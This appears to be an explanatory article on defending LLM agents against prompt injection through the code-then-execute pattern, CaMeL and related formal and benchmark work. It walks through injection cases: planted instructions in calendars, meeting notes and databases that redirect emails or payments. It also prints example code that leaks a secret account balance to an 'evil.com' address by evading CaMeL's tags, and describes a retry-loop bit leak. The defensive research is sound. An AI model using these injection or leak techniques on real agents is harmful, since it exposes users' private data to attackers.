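# The Code-Then-Execute Pattern for LLM Agents That Resist Prompt Injection

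## How the pattern works and how it relates to the other five

Code-then-execute is a design pattern meant to keep an attacker's text from choosing the actions of software agents that run on large language models (LLMs). The model writes a complete program from the user's request before the agent reads anything an outsider could have written. Ordinary software then runs the program, which handles the emails, web pages or files it fetches only as values. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, June 2025) named the pattern and presented it with five related ones. Researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich had described the best-known example, CaMeL ("capabilities for machine learning"), in March 2025.

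### Agents, tools and prompt injection

By itself, an LLM only produces text. An agent adds tools, which are functions that do things like read a calendar, search a mailbox or send a message. It also adds software that lets the model's text trigger those tools. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), a software developer's blog post, describes the usual loop. The developer instructs the model to print a line in a special syntax when the task calls for a search. A short program scans the output for that syntax, runs the search and pastes the results into the model's next prompt.

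Those results can contain text from anyone who can email the user. If a message in the inbox tells the assistant to forward last month's emails to some address, that instruction ends up in the same prompt as the user's request, and the model may follow it. This is called prompt injection, where text in an LLM's input makes it follow an attacker's instructions instead of the user's.

The name "prompt injection" alludes to SQL injection, an old attack in which text from a web form runs as a database command. Parameterised queries fully prevent SQL injection by guaranteeing that the database never interprets the supplied text as a command. LLMs have no counterpart, as David C explained in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. A model only predicts the next token (a word or part of one) from all the text so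 far, and nothing in that process distinguishes instructions from data. He advised designers to focus on deterministic safeguards outside the LLM, and cited the CaMeL and design-patterns papers as early work of that kind.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues hold the same view. Training or prompting a model to resist injections makes attacks less likely to succeed but can't rule them out, and they note that computer vision has struggled with a similar problem, adversarial examples, for over a decade. Filters that look for injections are often AI models too, so attackers can also get past them. Asking the user to confirm each sensitive action works in theory, but tired users approve unsafe ones. The remaining option is to constrain the system around the model so that the agent stays safe even when the model follows injected instructions.

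Models have become much harder to inject since then. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 reports that, on a fixed set of 1,804 attacks, an attacker with 15 attempts had a 1.0% chance of success. In a harder test, an automated attacker that had trained on the test's scenarios against earlier Claude models got 200 attempts at each. It succeeded at least once in 31 of 40 coding scenarios, and in 18 with Anthropic's injection detectors switched on. Anthropic describes this setting as deliberately permissive, since real attackers seldom know their target so well. Against Claude Sonnet 5, the attacker succeeded in at most 7 scenarios without the detectors. Even the good figures, though, only measure how often particular attackers succeeded. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, objected that a defence which stops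 99% of attacks still fails as security, because an attacker's job is to find the other 1%.

All six patterns follow the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted data, that data must have no way to trigger a consequential action. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think general-purpose agents are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees while they depend on the current kind of LLM, so their patterns deliberately restrict which tasks an agent can perform.

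### The calendar example

Suppose a user asks an assistant to "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe". With the variables renamed for readability, the program that Beurer-Kellner and colleagues give for this request is:

```
schedule = calendar.read(today)
message  = LLM("format this data", schedule)
email.write(message, "john.doe@company.com")
```

An LLM writes this program before anything has read the calendar, using only trusted information, which the example assumes includes the boss's address. An interpreter, which is ordinary software with no LLM in it, then runs the program. `calendar.read` fetches the day's entries and stores them as `schedule`. The `LLM` call passes them to another model instance, which has no tools, and stores its reply as `message`. Then `email.write` sends that text to John Doe.

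Anyone who can send the user an invitation can put text in the calendar. Suppose a stranger's invitation contains an order to email the user's contracts to an outside address. The LLM that formats the calendar entries reads this order, but the LLM that wrote the program never does. The formatting LLM may comply in full, but it can only change the text it returns. The interpreter places that text in the body of the email without searching it for commands. The program still contains a single `email.write`, and its recipient is a constant that the program-writing LLM set before the agent opened the invitation.

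The body of the email is less safe. An attacker can drop a meeting from the list, invent one, add a malicious link or write instructions for whatever assistant John Doe uses. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues say that the pattern cannot prevent this. It therefore falls short of their own standard, because they also want an agent's outputs to pose no risk downstream, and an email partly written by an attacker is a risk.

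The program's control flow is the choice and order of its tool calls, and its data flow is the movement of values into those calls. The pattern provides control-flow integrity, which *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) defines as confining execution to a program that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. The program may contain conditions, so untrusted data can determine which existing branch runs, but it cannot add a branch. For example, if a user asks the assistant to accept an invitation when the afternoon is free and decline it otherwise, a forged calendar entry can cause the assistant to decline. Control-flow integrity does not prevent this branch steering, so the possible harm depends on which branches the program contains.

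Writing code does not by itself protect an agent from prompt injection. *DADL* (2026), a paper on tool libraries for company agents, discusses a "Code Mode" in which the model acts through short JavaScript snippets, and warns that an injected prompt may introduce code that makes unexpected calls. Code-then-execute avoids this because the model finishes the program before any untrusted data arrives.

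### When the data supplies the recipient

In the calendar example, the user names the recipient. The CaMeL paper considers a less specific request, to send Bob the document he asked for in the last meeting. Both Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The paper uses this case to show a flaw in the earlier dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in April 2023.

That design splits the work between two LLMs. The privileged LLM takes the user's request and can use tools, but never receives untrusted content. The quarantined LLM processes the untrusted content and has no tools; the designer should expect it to "go rogue at any moment". A controller, which is ordinary software, passes things between them. When the user wants a summary of the latest email, the privileged LLM requests the email and the controller stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged LLM then requests a summary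 of `$VAR1`. The controller substitutes the real text, runs the quarantined LLM on it and stores the answer as `$VAR2`. The privileged LLM instructs the controller to display `$VAR2` without receiving the summary itself. Willison allowed the controller to pass the quarantined LLM's answer to the privileged LLM only when the task is to sort text into a fixed set of categories, because the controller can check that the answer is one of them.

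Written out as a program, the steps for Bob's document look roughly like this:

```
notes    = find_notes("last meeting")
title    = quarantined_llm("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
address  = quarantined_llm("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetch_document(title)
send_email(address, document)
```

Now suppose that someone with access to the notes has planted an instruction in them to give a different address for Bob. The quarantined LLM follows the instruction and returns the attacker's address. The interpreter makes the same five calls in the same order as it would have with unaltered notes, but the document goes to the attacker. No injected text reaches the privileged LLM, and control-flow integrity holds, because the attack works entirely through the data flow.

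Strict output formats, which Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend for every agent, do not help much here, because an attacker's email address would pass a check that the answer is an email address. The plain code-then-execute pattern has the same flaw, since it makes no difference whether the privileged LLM issues its steps one by one or writes them as a program beforehand.

### What CaMeL adds

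CaMeL keeps the two LLMs and also records where every value came from. The privileged LLM writes its program in a restricted version of Python, which CaMeL's designers chose because LLMs already write Python well. The restrictions exclude constructs such as arbitrary `while` loops, according to *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026). A custom interpreter parses the program into a tree of operations and executes it node by node, so CaMeL can control every assignment and call.

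The interpreter keeps a capability tag on each value, recording where the value came from and who may read it. Each value also carries the history of the values it was derived from. Since `address` comes from `notes`, and an outsider could have written in the notes, `address` counts as untrusted regardless of what the quarantined LLM returned.

Before a tool call runs, the interpreter checks it against a security policy. Nikolaou and colleagues describe the policy as a Python function that receives the call, its arguments and their tags, and returns "allow" or "deny" with a reason. Either of two policies would stop Bob's document from being emailed to the attacker, who is neither a trusted recipient nor permitted to read it. In Willison's account of CaMeL, `send_email` may run only if the recipient is trusted, and the system can ask the user to approve an unknown address. Peters-Gill and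 colleagues give the example of a rule that forbids emailing private data to anyone without permission to read it.

The two rules behave differently when nobody is attacking. A rule that requires a trusted recipient interrupts the user even over Bob's genuine address, unless the user has already listed it, because a tag shows only where an address came from and not whether it is correct. If Bob has permission to read the document, the rule about readers lets it through without interrupting the user. But if an attacker had corrupted `title` and left `address` alone, that rule would also let the wrong document through, provided Bob may read that one too.

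The CaMeL paper acknowledges that users must specify and maintain the security policies, and that it is hard to balance security against the fatigue of repeated approval requests. Willison welcomed CaMeL as the first mitigation he had seen that claims strong guarantees, but the policies made him nervous because he still has trouble thinking them through after two decades around application security. He was happier about the privacy benefit. Extracting an address is easier than planning, so the quarantined LLM can be a small model on the user's own machine, and the company that hosts the privileged LLM never sees the user's mail.

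The definition of code-then-execute includes none of this machinery. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues require only a "formal computer program" that may call tools and unprivileged LLMs, and they cite CaMeL as an instance. Their calendar program has no tags or policy. The pattern is easy to confuse with CaMeL, partly because of how Willison (2025) summarised it in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, a post that shares the paper's title. He described the pattern as code in a custom sandboxed language built for full data-flow analysis, which is how CaMeL works.

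*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) distinguishes two mechanisms. Dividing duties between a planning model and a reading model blocks attacks on control flow. Information-flow control, which labels data by origin and uses those labels to refuse data at sensitive calls, blocks attacks on data flow. The plain pattern has only the division of duties, while CaMeL has both mechanisms, though the CaMeL paper left a formal proof to later work. Likewise, under the definitions of Peters-Gill and colleagues, CaMeL's security reduces to control-flow integrity when it has no policies. A result about CaMeL therefore applies to code-then-execute in general only if it does not depend on CaMeL's labels and policies.

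### The six patterns compared

The patterns differ in what a model can read after untrusted data arrives, and this largely determines what an attacker can still do.

| Pattern | What the model sees after untrusted data arrives | What an attacker can still affect |
|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | Nothing new: no tool output returns to the model | The data that a fixed action works on; a hostile user can also influence which fixed action runs |
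| Plan-then-execute | The tool outputs, while the list of calls stays fixed | Any argument that the plan leaves open, such as an email's body |
| Map-reduce | One isolated model per document sees that document; the combining step gets only constrained answers, such as yes or no, if it uses an LLM | The answer about the attacker's own document |
| Dual LLM | The privileged LLM sees variable names or checked categories; the quarantined LLM sees the data | The contents of the variables, and so the arguments of calls that use them |
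| Code-then-execute | The LLM that wrote the program sees nothing more; quarantined LLMs see what the program passes them | Values that the program derives from the data, and which existing branch runs |
| Context-minimization | The results of a request, without the user's prompt | The request that the model derived from the prompt, and any untrusted text in the results |

Plan-then-execute is the most similar of the other five patterns. For the calendar request, the model commits to `calendar.read` followed by `email.write` to John Doe, then reads the calendar and fills in the email body. An injection cannot add a tool to the plan, but it can influence any argument the plan leaves blank. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues mention a file assistant that commits to the commands for finding and moving files, where an injection could still cause the model to look for sensitive files and copy them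 to a public drive. A program prevents much of this because it also fixes which value goes into which argument. It is also more flexible than a list of tool calls because it can loop over any number of meeting attendees or choose between two actions based on a result.

Code-then-execute takes the quarantine from the dual LLM pattern, and Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe it as that pattern taken "to its limit". Willison's privileged LLM requests one action, is told by the controller when it has finished, and then requests the next. In code-then-execute, the privileged LLM instead writes all the actions as one program before any of them runs, in a form that other software can analyse. CaMeL's tracking relies on this, and CaMeLoT, an extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, uses it to check a program against rules before any tool runs. However, the LLM sees no results, so it cannot react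 to them and has to anticipate every case that the program should handle.

The patterns in the table can be combined, and Beurer-Kellner and colleagues recommend doing so because they doubt that any single one will suffice for every threat. In map-reduce, for example, an agent that collects this month's invoices sends each file to its own isolated LLM, which answers only whether the file is an invoice. At worst, an attacker can get a malicious file counted as an invoice. A code-then-execute program can do the same in a loop, which limits an attacker to the same influence. The action-selector is the strictest of the six patterns and also the least capable, because an agent that never sees a tool's output cannot summarise an email or act on search results.

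### Injections in the user's own prompt

Context-minimization defends against a different attacker, who is either the user or someone whose text the user has pasted in. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues imagine a customer who asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and includes an instruction to give a large discount. The system first has the model turn the request into a database query. It then deletes the customer's prompt from the model's context, so the instruction is gone when the model writes its answer from the query's results.

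Code-then-execute has no such step, because it treats the user's prompt as the source of the program's authority. If a user copies text from an attacker's web page into the request, the LLM that writes the program reads it as part of the instruction and can include the attacker's calls in the program, which the interpreter will then execute. Willison raised the same concern about his privileged LLM in 2023. CaMeL's tags do not reliably help either. In the scheme of Nikolaou and colleagues, constants in a program count as trusted, so an attacker's address copied from the prompt would satisfy a rule that requires only a trusted recipient. A rule restricting who may read the document could still stop the email.

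The "user" may also be another agent. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents, without security policies, in which an orchestrator delegates work to a database agent and a notification agent. They planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address, then asked the system to send Julie a summary of all job applicants on Slack. All three agents kept to their own programs, and those of the database agent and the orchestrator were the same as in a run without the attack. But the orchestrator put the summary into its request to the notification agent, whose privileged LLM treated that request as its user's instruction and wrote a program with one more call, an email to the attacker.

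## What proofs show about the guarantee

In their abstract, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues promise "provable resistance" to prompt injection, but they argue for it informally, explaining what each pattern stops an injection from doing. When an agent fixes its plan in advance, they call the protection a form of "control flow integrity", a systems security term for keeping a running program on the paths that a predefined policy allows. Later papers supply definitions and machine-checked theorems, mostly for designs closely related to code-then-execute.

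### The argument for control-flow integrity

Peters-Gill and colleagues define control-flow integrity as confining an agent to a program based only on trusted information. They call such a program a control-flow plan. Given the values that the tools return, the plan determines which tool calls happen and in what order.

A program written before exposure to untrusted data meets this definition almost immediately. Let `u` be the user's request, `t` the trusted tool descriptions and `d` all the untrusted data that the tools will return:

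```
p     = write(u, t)
calls = run(p, d)
```

The privileged LLM writes `p`, and the interpreter runs it. Since `d` is not an input to `write`, changing `d` cannot change `p`. An attacker who controls every byte of `d` can still only select among the sequences of calls that `p` allows. The argument does not depend on how well the LLM resists injection, so it holds for weak and strong models alike.

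The guarantee does depend on the system around the model. The request and the tool descriptions must be free of the attacker's text, and the interpreter must never run a value as code. The LLM must also not rewrite the program in response to what happened when it ran. CaMeL relaxes this last condition. When a program fails, CaMeL tries again using the error message, which can depend on untrusted data. CaMeL censors these messages to limit the effect, but Garby and colleagues point out that this censoring has no formal guarantee.

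Even when all the conditions hold, `run(p, d)` depends on `d`, so the attacker can still corrupt values, as with Bob's address, and affect which branches run. The attacker can also affect how many times a loop runs, for example by adding an invoice to a folder when the program pays every invoice in it.

Branches can also leak information. If a program sends one fixed message when an account balance is high and a different one when it is low, the recipient learns something about the balance although neither message contains it. This is called an implicit flow. Control-flow integrity does not prevent it, so CaMeL relies on its tags and policies to do so.

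### Two leaks in CaMeL's tags

Garby and colleagues found two ways for a secret to get past CaMeL's tags. Their example is an agent that manages a customer's bank account, where the balance is secret. The simplest attempt to reveal it would be:

```
if account.balance > threshold:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL blocks this. The condition reads the balance, so the interpreter treats the email as dependent on a secret and refuses to send it. However, a program can pass the same information through two variables:

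```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when an assignment runs under a secret condition, but it does nothing when the program skips that assignment. The two possible runs look like this:

| | Balance above the threshold | Balance at or below it |
|---|---|---|
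| `tmp` at the second `if` | False, secret | True, public |
| `rich` at the third `if` | True, public | False, public |
| Email | Sent | Not sent |

When the balance is high, `tmp` is secret and false, so the program skips `rich = False` and `rich` keeps its public tag. CaMeL then treats the final condition as public and lets the email through. The attacker receives it exactly when the balance is above the threshold. Garby and colleagues trace the trick to a classic example by Fenton. The standard remedy, "no high upgrade", halts any program that tries to change a public variable under a secret condition. Here, a high balance would halt the program at `tmp = False`, and no email would go out whether the balance was high or low.

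The other leak is in the retry loop. Whether CaMeL refuses a call can depend on a secret, so a refusal can reveal one bit. Most information-flow systems allow a leak of that size. But CaMeL's retry loop is ordinary Python outside the interpreter, so no tag tracks the information each refusal passes to the loop. A program could test one binary digit of the balance on each attempt, triggering a refusal whenever the digit is 1, and so reveal a 32-bit balance in 32 attempts.

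Both leaks require a program whose structure allows them. In code-then-execute, an attacker who controls only the data cannot write such a program, so neither leak breaks control-flow integrity. The leaks matter when the attacker's text has reached the user's request, because the tags are then the main remaining defence. They also matter if a program written without malicious intent happens to have the same structure.

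### A theorem that covers every program

Garby and colleagues respond with a small programming language, the LLMbda calculus, whose tracking also covers the retry loop. It extends the lambda calculus, a minimal language built from functions, with operations for prompting a model and for forking or clearing a conversation. A quarantined LLM is then a prompt inside a forked and cleared conversation rather than a fixed part of the architecture.

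In the main examples, a value's label marks it as untrusted, secret, both or neither. A value computed inside a branch inherits the label of the branch's condition. This limits branch steering. If untrusted data determined which branch ran, even a constant inside it counts as untrusted, and a tool that requires trusted arguments will reject it. The same rule covers code that a model writes after reading an attacker's email. The code runs under the label of that conversation, so everything it computes is untrusted.

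The main theorem is a form of noninterference, the property that what an observer sees does not depend on inputs that should not affect it. Take an observer who can see only values with labels up to some level `m`. Two starting points are indistinguishable to this observer, written `~ₘ`, if they differ only in values that the observer cannot see. Because an LLM's replies are random, ideal noninterference would require both starting points to give every visible result the same probability. Garby and colleagues prove a slightly weaker property, for every level `m` and every program in the language:

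```
if    C₀ ~ₘ C₁  and  e₀ ~ₘ e₁
then  some ω with total at most 1 satisfies
      ⟦pc ⊢ C₀, e₀⟧ₘ ≤ ω   and   ⟦pc ⊢ C₁, e₁⟧ₘ ≤ ω
```

Here `C` is the conversation so far, `e` is the program and `pc` is the label of any conditions already in force. The double brackets are the probabilities of the results that the observer can distinguish. These may add up to less than 1, and the shortfall is the probability that the program never finishes. By the theorem, a single set of probabilities, `ω`, is at least as large as both sets.

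For example, suppose with one secret the observer sees "yes" half the time and the program hangs the other half. With another secret, the observer sees "yes" half the time and "no" half the time. The theorem permits this, because the second set of probabilities can serve as `ω`. It rules out a program that produces "yes" 80% of the time with one secret and "no" 80% of the time with another, because `ω` would then have to total at least 1.6.

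The guarantee is "termination-insensitive", meaning that a secret may influence whether the program finishes, but nothing else that the observer sees. A failed policy check counts as not finishing, so a refusal can still reveal something. Garby and colleagues also bound this leak by showing that the statistical distance between the two sets of results is at most the average of the two probabilities of not finishing. In the permitted example, both figures are 0.25. For a program that always finishes, the distance is zero.

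The bound applies to a single run, so an untracked loop that kept restarting the program could recreate CaMeL's problem. Randori, the agent Garby and colleagues built in the language, avoids this by repairing its program against artificial tool responses until the program works, and only then running it on the real data.

The proof uses an imaginary second version of the language. As soon as a computation's label rises beyond what the observer can see, this version skips the computation and returns a dummy value. It never uses the hidden values, so it gives the same probabilities from both starting points. It also finishes at least as often as the real version, so its probabilities are at least as large. The proof uses these probabilities as `ω`.

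Lean, a proof assistant, checked the theorem. It also checked that the interpreter matches the mathematical definition of the language, assuming that the LLM's replies to a given conversation follow a fixed probability distribution. The proofs therefore cover the software that calls the LLM. CaMeL has no equivalent proofs because its tracking rules exist only as Python code.

### What endorsement gives up

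Strict labels also block legitimate tasks. Garby and colleagues give the example request "find my friend's payment details from their website and send them $50". The account details come from a web page, so they are untrusted, and a payment tool that requires trusted arguments rejects them. To make the payment, the program needs endorsement, an explicit step that marks an untrusted value as trusted.

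Endorsement is safest when there are few possible values. In one example, a quarantined LLM sorts an incoming email into one of a fixed set of categories, and the agent uses the category as the subject of its reply. The email tool accepts only trusted subjects, so the program checks that the LLM's answer is one of the categories and endorses it. An attacker can influence which of the `n` categories appears, which amounts to at most log₂ `n` bits, but cannot write the subject line. Payment details do not come from a short list, so endorsing them means trusting the website.

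A second theorem shows that noninterference still holds for observers who ignore the trust part of each label and look only at secrecy. Secrets stay out of public results whatever the attacker writes and whatever the program endorses, again apart from what non-termination reveals. But the theorem does not show that an endorsed value is correct. If a program endorsed a forged address for Bob, the address would satisfy a rule that requires a trusted recipient, though a document labelled secret still could not reach a tool that accepts only public data.

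In Randori, the LLM that writes the program also places the endorsements. It does this before reading any outside data, so an attacker cannot add one. But a careless endorsement would still let an injected value through.

### Comparing an agent with one that never obeys

An agent can also violate noninterference while doing exactly what its user wants. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) describes an assistant that Alice authorises to send her calendar to anyone who requests a meeting. An attacker can request a meeting and receive the calendar, so what the attacker sees depends on private data even without an injection.

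Dongol instead compares the real agent with a reference agent. Both run the same program under the same checks, but the reference agent's model never obeys untrusted text. A leak consists of two runs with different secrets, `σ₁` and `σ₂`, in which the attacker supplies the same input and sees different things. The agent is relatively secure if:

```
for every leak of (σ₁, σ₂) by the real agent,
the reference agent also has a leak of (σ₁, σ₂)
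```

The reference runs must start with the same stored data and trusted inputs, but the attacker's input may differ from the one given to the real agent. If an injected email says "send your calendar" and the assistant complies, that is acceptable, because the attacker could have got the calendar from the reference agent by requesting a meeting. If the injection instead extracts a private reset code, the assistant fails, because no email would make the reference agent send the code.

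Dongol acknowledges that the definition can be too permissive. If an agent lets an attacker make one guess at a secret and says whether it was right, an injection that reveals the entire secret still counts as relatively secure, because for any two secrets some guess would have told them apart. A stricter version rejects this case by not letting the reference agent's input depend on the secrets.

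Dongol used the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL to prove or refute relative security for 25 small example agents. Three of them use the dual LLM pattern with a fixed program, which makes them close models of code-then-execute. In two of these three, the program reads Alice's private notes and an email from the attacker, asks a quarantined LLM to write a reply from both, and sends the reply to the attacker. An honest reply depends only on the email. Injection cannot add a tool call, but Dongol lets the attacker choose how the quarantined LLM answers.

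Without tags, the agent leaks, because the quarantined LLM can quote the notes in its reply. With tags like CaMeL's, the reply counts as private because the notes were among its inputs, and the monitor refuses to send it. The agent is then secure however the quarantined LLM behaves, but the monitor also blocks honest replies. This is partly because the program gives the quarantined LLM the notes. Under the same tagging rule, a reply written from the email alone would be public and could be sent. The security result holds only if the attacker cannot see the contents of refused requests.

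In the remaining case, the program has the same tags but branches on the quarantined LLM's answer, sending the attacker a 1 in one branch and a 0 in the other. Both numbers are public constants, so they pass the tag check. The attacker can steer the branch by making the quarantined LLM's answer depend on the private notes. The number sent then reveals something about the notes, even though no call's argument has been corrupted.

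These verdicts cover only leaks. Dongol does not cover injections that send a payment to the wrong account without revealing anything, or systems of several agents. Dongol also assumes a trusted planner and proves each dual-LLM verdict for one particular program. The tags model CaMeL's normal mode. Dongol leaves to future work CaMeL's strict mode, which tags values with the conditions controlling them to close the branch channel. The bank-balance example suggests that strict mode would help but not be enough. CaMeL blocked the direct version, so its tags must have been following conditions, but the version with two variables still got through.

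### Labels in a loop, and checks before the run

Labels can also protect an agent that does not write its program in advance. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft system in which an LLM still chooses one tool call at a time. If a tool's result is less trusted or more confidential than the conversation so far, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the LLM only the variable's name. The LLM can have a quarantined LLM process the contents, or it can open the variable itself. Opening an untrusted variable makes the conversation untrusted, and a policy can then block consequential calls. The LLM can therefore react to what it reads, unlike one that has to write the whole program in advance, but the policy may block the calls it needs to act on that information.

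Costa and colleagues prove that such a loop can enforce explicit secrecy, meaning that for any given sequence of steps, secret data does not flow directly into public outputs. The choice of sequence may still reveal something about that data. Garby and colleagues describe the result as noninterference for one specific loop, but Costa and colleagues say noninterference would be too restrictive, because it would essentially forbid publicly visible calls after the agent reads a secret. Dongol notes that the program that leaks through its 1 and 0 satisfies explicit secrecy.

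FIDES can also relax its rules for small answers. A policy may let a yes-or-no answer from untrusted text influence a consequential call, because the answer carries only one bit. This resembles endorsing an email's category, but no explicit step in a program marks the exception. Garby and colleagues object that an auditor examining a particular run cannot tell an intended exception from a real leak.

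CaMeLoT, the extension of CaMeL by Nikolaou and colleagues, takes advantage of having the whole program available before it runs. It converts the program into a finite-state machine, a map of the steps the program could take, and marks which values are untrusted at each step. A model checker, which is software that searches every path through such a map, then tests rules like this one:

```
AG(call_send_direct_message ⇒ recipient_trusted)
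```

`AG` means "at every point on every path", so the rule forbids any direct message to an untrusted recipient. If a program extracts Bob's address from channel messages and sends a message to it, CaMeLoT rejects the program before any tool has read the channel messages. The privileged LLM then receives a description of the offending path and tries to repair the program. This kind of retry does not expose the LLM to untrusted data because the description comes only from the program.

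The map leaves out the conditions on branches and loops, so it treats every path through them as possible. An attacker who steers branches can do no more than choose among these paths, so a program passes only if none of them breaks the rule. CaMeLoT can also check the order of actions, such as requiring approval before an agent disconnects a computer from the network. Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven unsafe plans for a security analyst's agent, each breaking a different rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified CaMeL that tracked only untrusted values caught one. They expected this result because they had chosen rules that CaMeL's checks on individual calls can't express.

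Checking in advance has its own limits. CaMeLoT could reproduce 22 of the 28 policies written for CaMeL's benchmark tasks. Most of the other six depend on facts available only during the run, such as who can read a shared file, so CaMeL still has to check them then. CaMeLoT also treats a value as untrusted whenever its origin is uncertain, so it can reject a safe program. For example, a calendar entry's description may be trustworthy if the user wrote it, but the program does not show who did.

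## What benchmark experiments measured

Most experiments on code-then-execute use AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, banking, chat and travel tasks. It pairs each user task with several attacks, which plant instructions in the emails, files or web pages that the agent will read. Automatic checks measure the agent's utility, the share of user tasks it completes, and the attack success rate, the share of attacked runs in which the attacker achieves their goal.

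### Banking tasks with and without policies

Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL and their own agent, Randori, on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks. Each agent was to attempt every task three times without an attack (48 runs) and three times under each of nine attacks (432 runs).

They also checked whether the program for the user's task could contain the tool call or file that the attack needs, for each of the 144 pairs of task and attack. In 97 pairs, it never would. If the user asks for a summary of recent transactions, for example, the program has no payment for an attacker to redirect. In the other 47 pairs, it could. Writing the program first should therefore defeat about two thirds of these attacks without any tags or policies.

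| Agent | Model | Tasks completed without attack (95% interval) | Attacks resisted, 97 pairs | Attacks resisted, 47 pairs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, no policies | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 (66.7% ± 23.4) | 98 of 99 | 141 of 141 |
| CaMeL, no policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 (70.8% ± 21.4) | 240 of 241 | 138 of 141 |
| CaMeL, policies | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 (37.5% ± 26.6) | 97 of 97 | 134 of 134 |
| CaMeL, policies | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 (37.5% ± 26.6) | 216 of 216 | 141 of 141 |
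| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 (75.0% ± 18.9) | 291 of 291 | 139 of 141 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 36 of 48 (75.0% ± 20.0) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 (64.6% ± 22.0) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| Randori, no endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 30 of 48 (62.5% ± 24.2) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |
| Randori, no endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 26 of 48 (54.2% ± 23.3) | 291 of 291 | 141 of 141 |

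CaMeL's attack figures exclude attacked runs that never finished. Among the runs that finished, five attacks succeeded without policies and none with them. But the policies almost halved the number of tasks CaMeL completed.

The intervals are wide because 16 tasks are a small sample. With GPT-5.2, CaMeL's utility could be anywhere from 43% to 90% without policies and from 11% to 64% with them. These ranges overlap, but another team found an even larger drop on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks. In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) report that CaMeL completed 13 to 17 of these tasks without policies, depending on the model, and 4 to 6 with policies. CaMeL's strict mode, which follows conditions more closely, gave nearly the same results as its normal mode. The perfect security scores are also uncertain, because resisting all 141 attacks over 47 pairs is compatible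 with a true rate as low as 92.4%.

Randori completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies, even though Randori checked its labels throughout. Randori enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies and its LLM can endorse untrusted values, so comparing it to CaMeL with policies is not quite even. Without endorsement, Randori completed five or six fewer runs and could no longer do tasks such as paying a bill whose amount and payee are in a file.

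Endorsement also let through the only two successful attacks in Randori's 1,296 attacked runs. Both came from the same pair, in which the user asks the agent to make a payment described in a file and the attacker has replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Refusing endorsement stops this attack but also prevents the genuine payment.

### A program that takes orders from a file

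Two of the five attacks that succeeded against CaMeL without policies belonged to the 97 pairs that should have been safe. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged LLM could not see the instructions, so it wrote a program that could carry out whatever they turned out to be. In outline, such a program looks like this:

```
for step in quarantined_llm("List the instructions", file):
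    if step.action == "pay":
        send_money(step.recipient, step.amount)
    elif step.action == "change password":
        update_password(step.value)
    # and so on, with a branch for each tool
```

Garby and colleagues call this an "interpreter loop". An attacker who can edit the file can choose the calls, their order and their arguments, much as in an agent with no protection. Control-flow integrity still holds, because the program depends only on the user's request. The attack is an extreme case of branch steering, in which the existing branches cover almost everything the agent can do. The guarantee becomes less useful as the program becomes broader, and the user's request here called for a very broad one. CaMeL's policies can still block individual calls, and no attack succeeded in the finished runs with these policies.

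### Agents that read between steps

Two other systems let the LLM read some results and then write more code, so they lose the protection of writing the whole program first. They rely instead on a programming language's type system, which checks code before it runs, and on some checks at runtime.

Zhou and colleagues built ELBA, which Garby and colleagues discuss under the name TypeGuard. Its LLM writes a Haskell program, and the type checker rejects the program if it could perform an action the developer didn't allow. The program can pass what it has read to another LLM call, which writes the next piece of code under the same or stricter restrictions. For the Slack tasks, the policies lower a model's privileges to those of the least trusted source it has read.

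With policies on and no attack, ELBA completed 8 to 10 of the 21 Slack tasks, about twice as many as CaMeL. Without policies, ELBA completed 14 to 18 and CaMeL 13 to 17. Reacting to data therefore seems to help most when policies are on, though the two systems also enforce different policies.

All four models resisted all of AgentDojo's own attacks even without policies, so those attacks could not show a difference in security between the two systems. Zhou and colleagues therefore simulated the worst case in ELBA by deleting the model's real task whenever its input contained a planted instruction, leaving only the attacker's text. Without policies, between 16% and 42% of these injections succeeded, depending on the model. With policies, ELBA resisted all 735 injections for each model but completed far fewer of the users' tasks, for example 351 instead of 523 with Claude Opus 4.7.

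They did not run this test on CaMeL, but they expect it to do well because its choice of tool calls does not depend on the data. Without policies, the data can still change the arguments of those calls, as with Bob's document.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system that uses Scala. The LLM submits one snippet at a time and reads the results, except for secret data, which stays in a wrapper that the LLM's code can process but not reveal. The compiler rejects any snippet that would use a file, network connection or other resource without permission. In a test with secrets in a project folder, neither of two models leaked any when the wrapper was on. When the secrets were stored as plain text, one of the models, MiniMax M2.5, leaked them in 8 of 11 runs in which the user's own request was malicious.

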